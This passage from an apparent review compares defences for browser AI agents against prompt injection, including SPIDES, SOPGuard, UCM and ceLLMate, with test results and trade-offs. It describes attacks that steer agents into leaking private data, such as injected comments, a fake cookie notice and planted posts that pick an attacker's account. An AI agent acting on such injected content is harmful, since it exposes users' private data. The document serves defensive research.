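| Opening an address, clicking or submitting a form on a trusted site | No untrusted content could have influenced the action |
| The same actions on any other site, or filling in a field anywhere | No untrusted content could have influenced the action, or the receiving site may read all the data involved |
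| Running code on a page | Never |

The third rule lets the agent send private data to a new site if no attacker could have influenced the decision. Zverev and colleagues reason that the transfer must then follow from the user's request.

In the running example, the agent can get a summary of the discussion without reading the comment. If it reads the comment, its context becomes untrusted, and it then needs approval to open the mailbox. If the code is already in the context, the agent needs approval to open the attacker's URL, because SPIDES treats navigation as sending data and the attacker's site is not a permitted reader. SPIDES's rules cover only browser tools, so images in the chat window still need a separate control.

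The researchers tested SPIDES on 28 simulated websites with 56 ordinary tasks, 56 attacks and five models, including GPT-5.6 Sol and Claude Opus 5.5. When an attacker's instruction reached the main model, the test software replaced the model's next actions with the attacker's. The results therefore measure how well SPIDES protects against attacks when the model does not resist injected instructions. The ranges below cover the five models, and some are calculated from the study's results for different types of task and attack.

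| Defence | Tasks completed | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| None | 58–91% | 57–96% |
| SOPGuard | 58–93% | 53–73% |
| UCM | 43–68% | 5–7% |
| SPIDES | 67–86% | 0% |

SOPGuard did badly here because many of the attacks stayed within one site or made the agent do something harmful without moving data between sites, and it was not designed to stop either kind. Opus 5.5 completed more tasks with SPIDES than with no defence, partly because SPIDES hid login details and other private documents from the model, so its safety filters triggered fewer refusals.

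The result of zero depends on correct labels and on the user's approval decisions. The researchers assumed a user who approved every safe request and denied every request the attacker had influenced. SPIDES averaged 1.84 approvals per completed task, compared with 0.22 for SOPGuard. Someone who used SPIDES for 20 such tasks a day would face about 37 requests, enough for approval to become a habit.

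SPIDES can also require approval less often than SOPGuard. In one harmless task, the agent had to look up a product from one website on another website. SOPGuard required approval in all 25 runs, while SPIDES required it in four.

A leak can still occur when the attacker and the private data are on the same site. SPIDES records which sites may read a piece of data, but it cannot always distinguish between people within a site. In the attack on the public profile, the rules allowed the agent to type the recovery address into the profile. SPIDES prevented the leak because the agent also had to click "Save changes". If an attacker shared a document that saved automatically, the agent could type text into it from one of the user's private documents on the same site without needing that click.

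### False data that changes a permitted action

An attacker may not need to add an instruction if false information can make the agent choose the wrong permitted action. Foerster and colleagues call one form of this attack "branch steering". A NOVA plan usually includes a step that closes any cookie notice. The researchers made an advert look like a cookie notice, and the quarantined model identified it as one. The agent then clicked it, as the plan allowed, and was taken to the attacker's website. If a later step entered personal details, the attacker could receive them.

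The researchers tried comparing the screenshot with the page's code and using a second model to confirm what was on the screen. Versions of the attack got past both checks. Making the second model stricter blocked more attacks but also more harmless actions. ceLLMate could help because it would block a request to a site outside the user's task, whatever the button looked like.

False data can also change a choice within a permitted site. UCM lets the quarantined model pick an item from a list, and Nikolić and colleagues found that an attacker could make it pick the wrong one. Suppose a user asks the agent to share a private file with the person who reported a fault. An attacker's post could make the quarantined model pick the attacker's account. That account would be a valid item from the list, and sharing the file would be the action the user requested.

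SPIDES labels such an answer as untrusted and asks the user before the agent acts on it. This stopped all six attacks of this type in its tests, while UCM let through 43 to 63 per cent, depending on the model. But the user still has to notice that the account is wrong.

Qu, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity*, use the term "judgment integrity" for the missing protection. An agent has it if irrelevant text from an attacker never changes its decisions. For a request $q$, the data $d$ that the agent must read and an irrelevant addition $\delta$, the decision $J$ should satisfy

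$$J(q, d \oplus \delta) = J(q, d),$$

where $d \oplus \delta$ is the data with the attacker's text added. Qu and colleagues credit CaMeL with fully protecting the agent's instructions and data flows, but not its judgement. Labels can show that a decision relied on a stranger's review. They cannot show whether the review is true.

### Choosing between the designs

| Design | What the user must trust | Who sets the rules | What it checks | Main loss of usefulness | When it asks the user |
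|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| SOPGuard | A model's account of its sources | Fixed: data stays on its own origin | Text written into pages | None detected | When text crosses origins |
| Chrome | The gating function and critic | Google, applied to each task | Origins, actions and URLs written by the model | No published figures | Before sensitive steps |
| ceLLMate | The sitemap, the policies and a model's selection | Sites or administrators | Web requests | Refuses vague requests | Once before the task |
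| CaMeL with NOVA | The planning model | The planner, from the user's request | The order and type of actions | Many failed tasks | Not in the tests |
| UCM | Honest sites and correct labels | Site owners | Untrusted text entering the agent's context | Little access to free text | Before revealing free text |
| SPIDES | Listed sites and their labels | Site owners label, and the user lists trusted sites | Navigation, clicks and typing | Some failed tasks | When an action breaks a rule |

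SOPGuard is the easiest of the research designs to add to an existing browser because it needs nothing from websites. It suits an agent that carries private data between sites, but must be combined with another defence for URLs and for attacks within a mailbox. ceLLMate covers more channels and could complement SOPGuard, since it checks what a request does rather than where text came from.

SPIDES gives the broadest protection in these tests, but websites do not yet supply the labels it needs. Its developers compare labeling a site to adding accessibility information, which many sites already provide. A large email service could afford to add the labels and has a reason to protect its users, but a small forum may never add them. If the user leaves that forum off the trusted list, SPIDES treats even the user's private messages there as public, so the agent could leak them to another site without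 asking.
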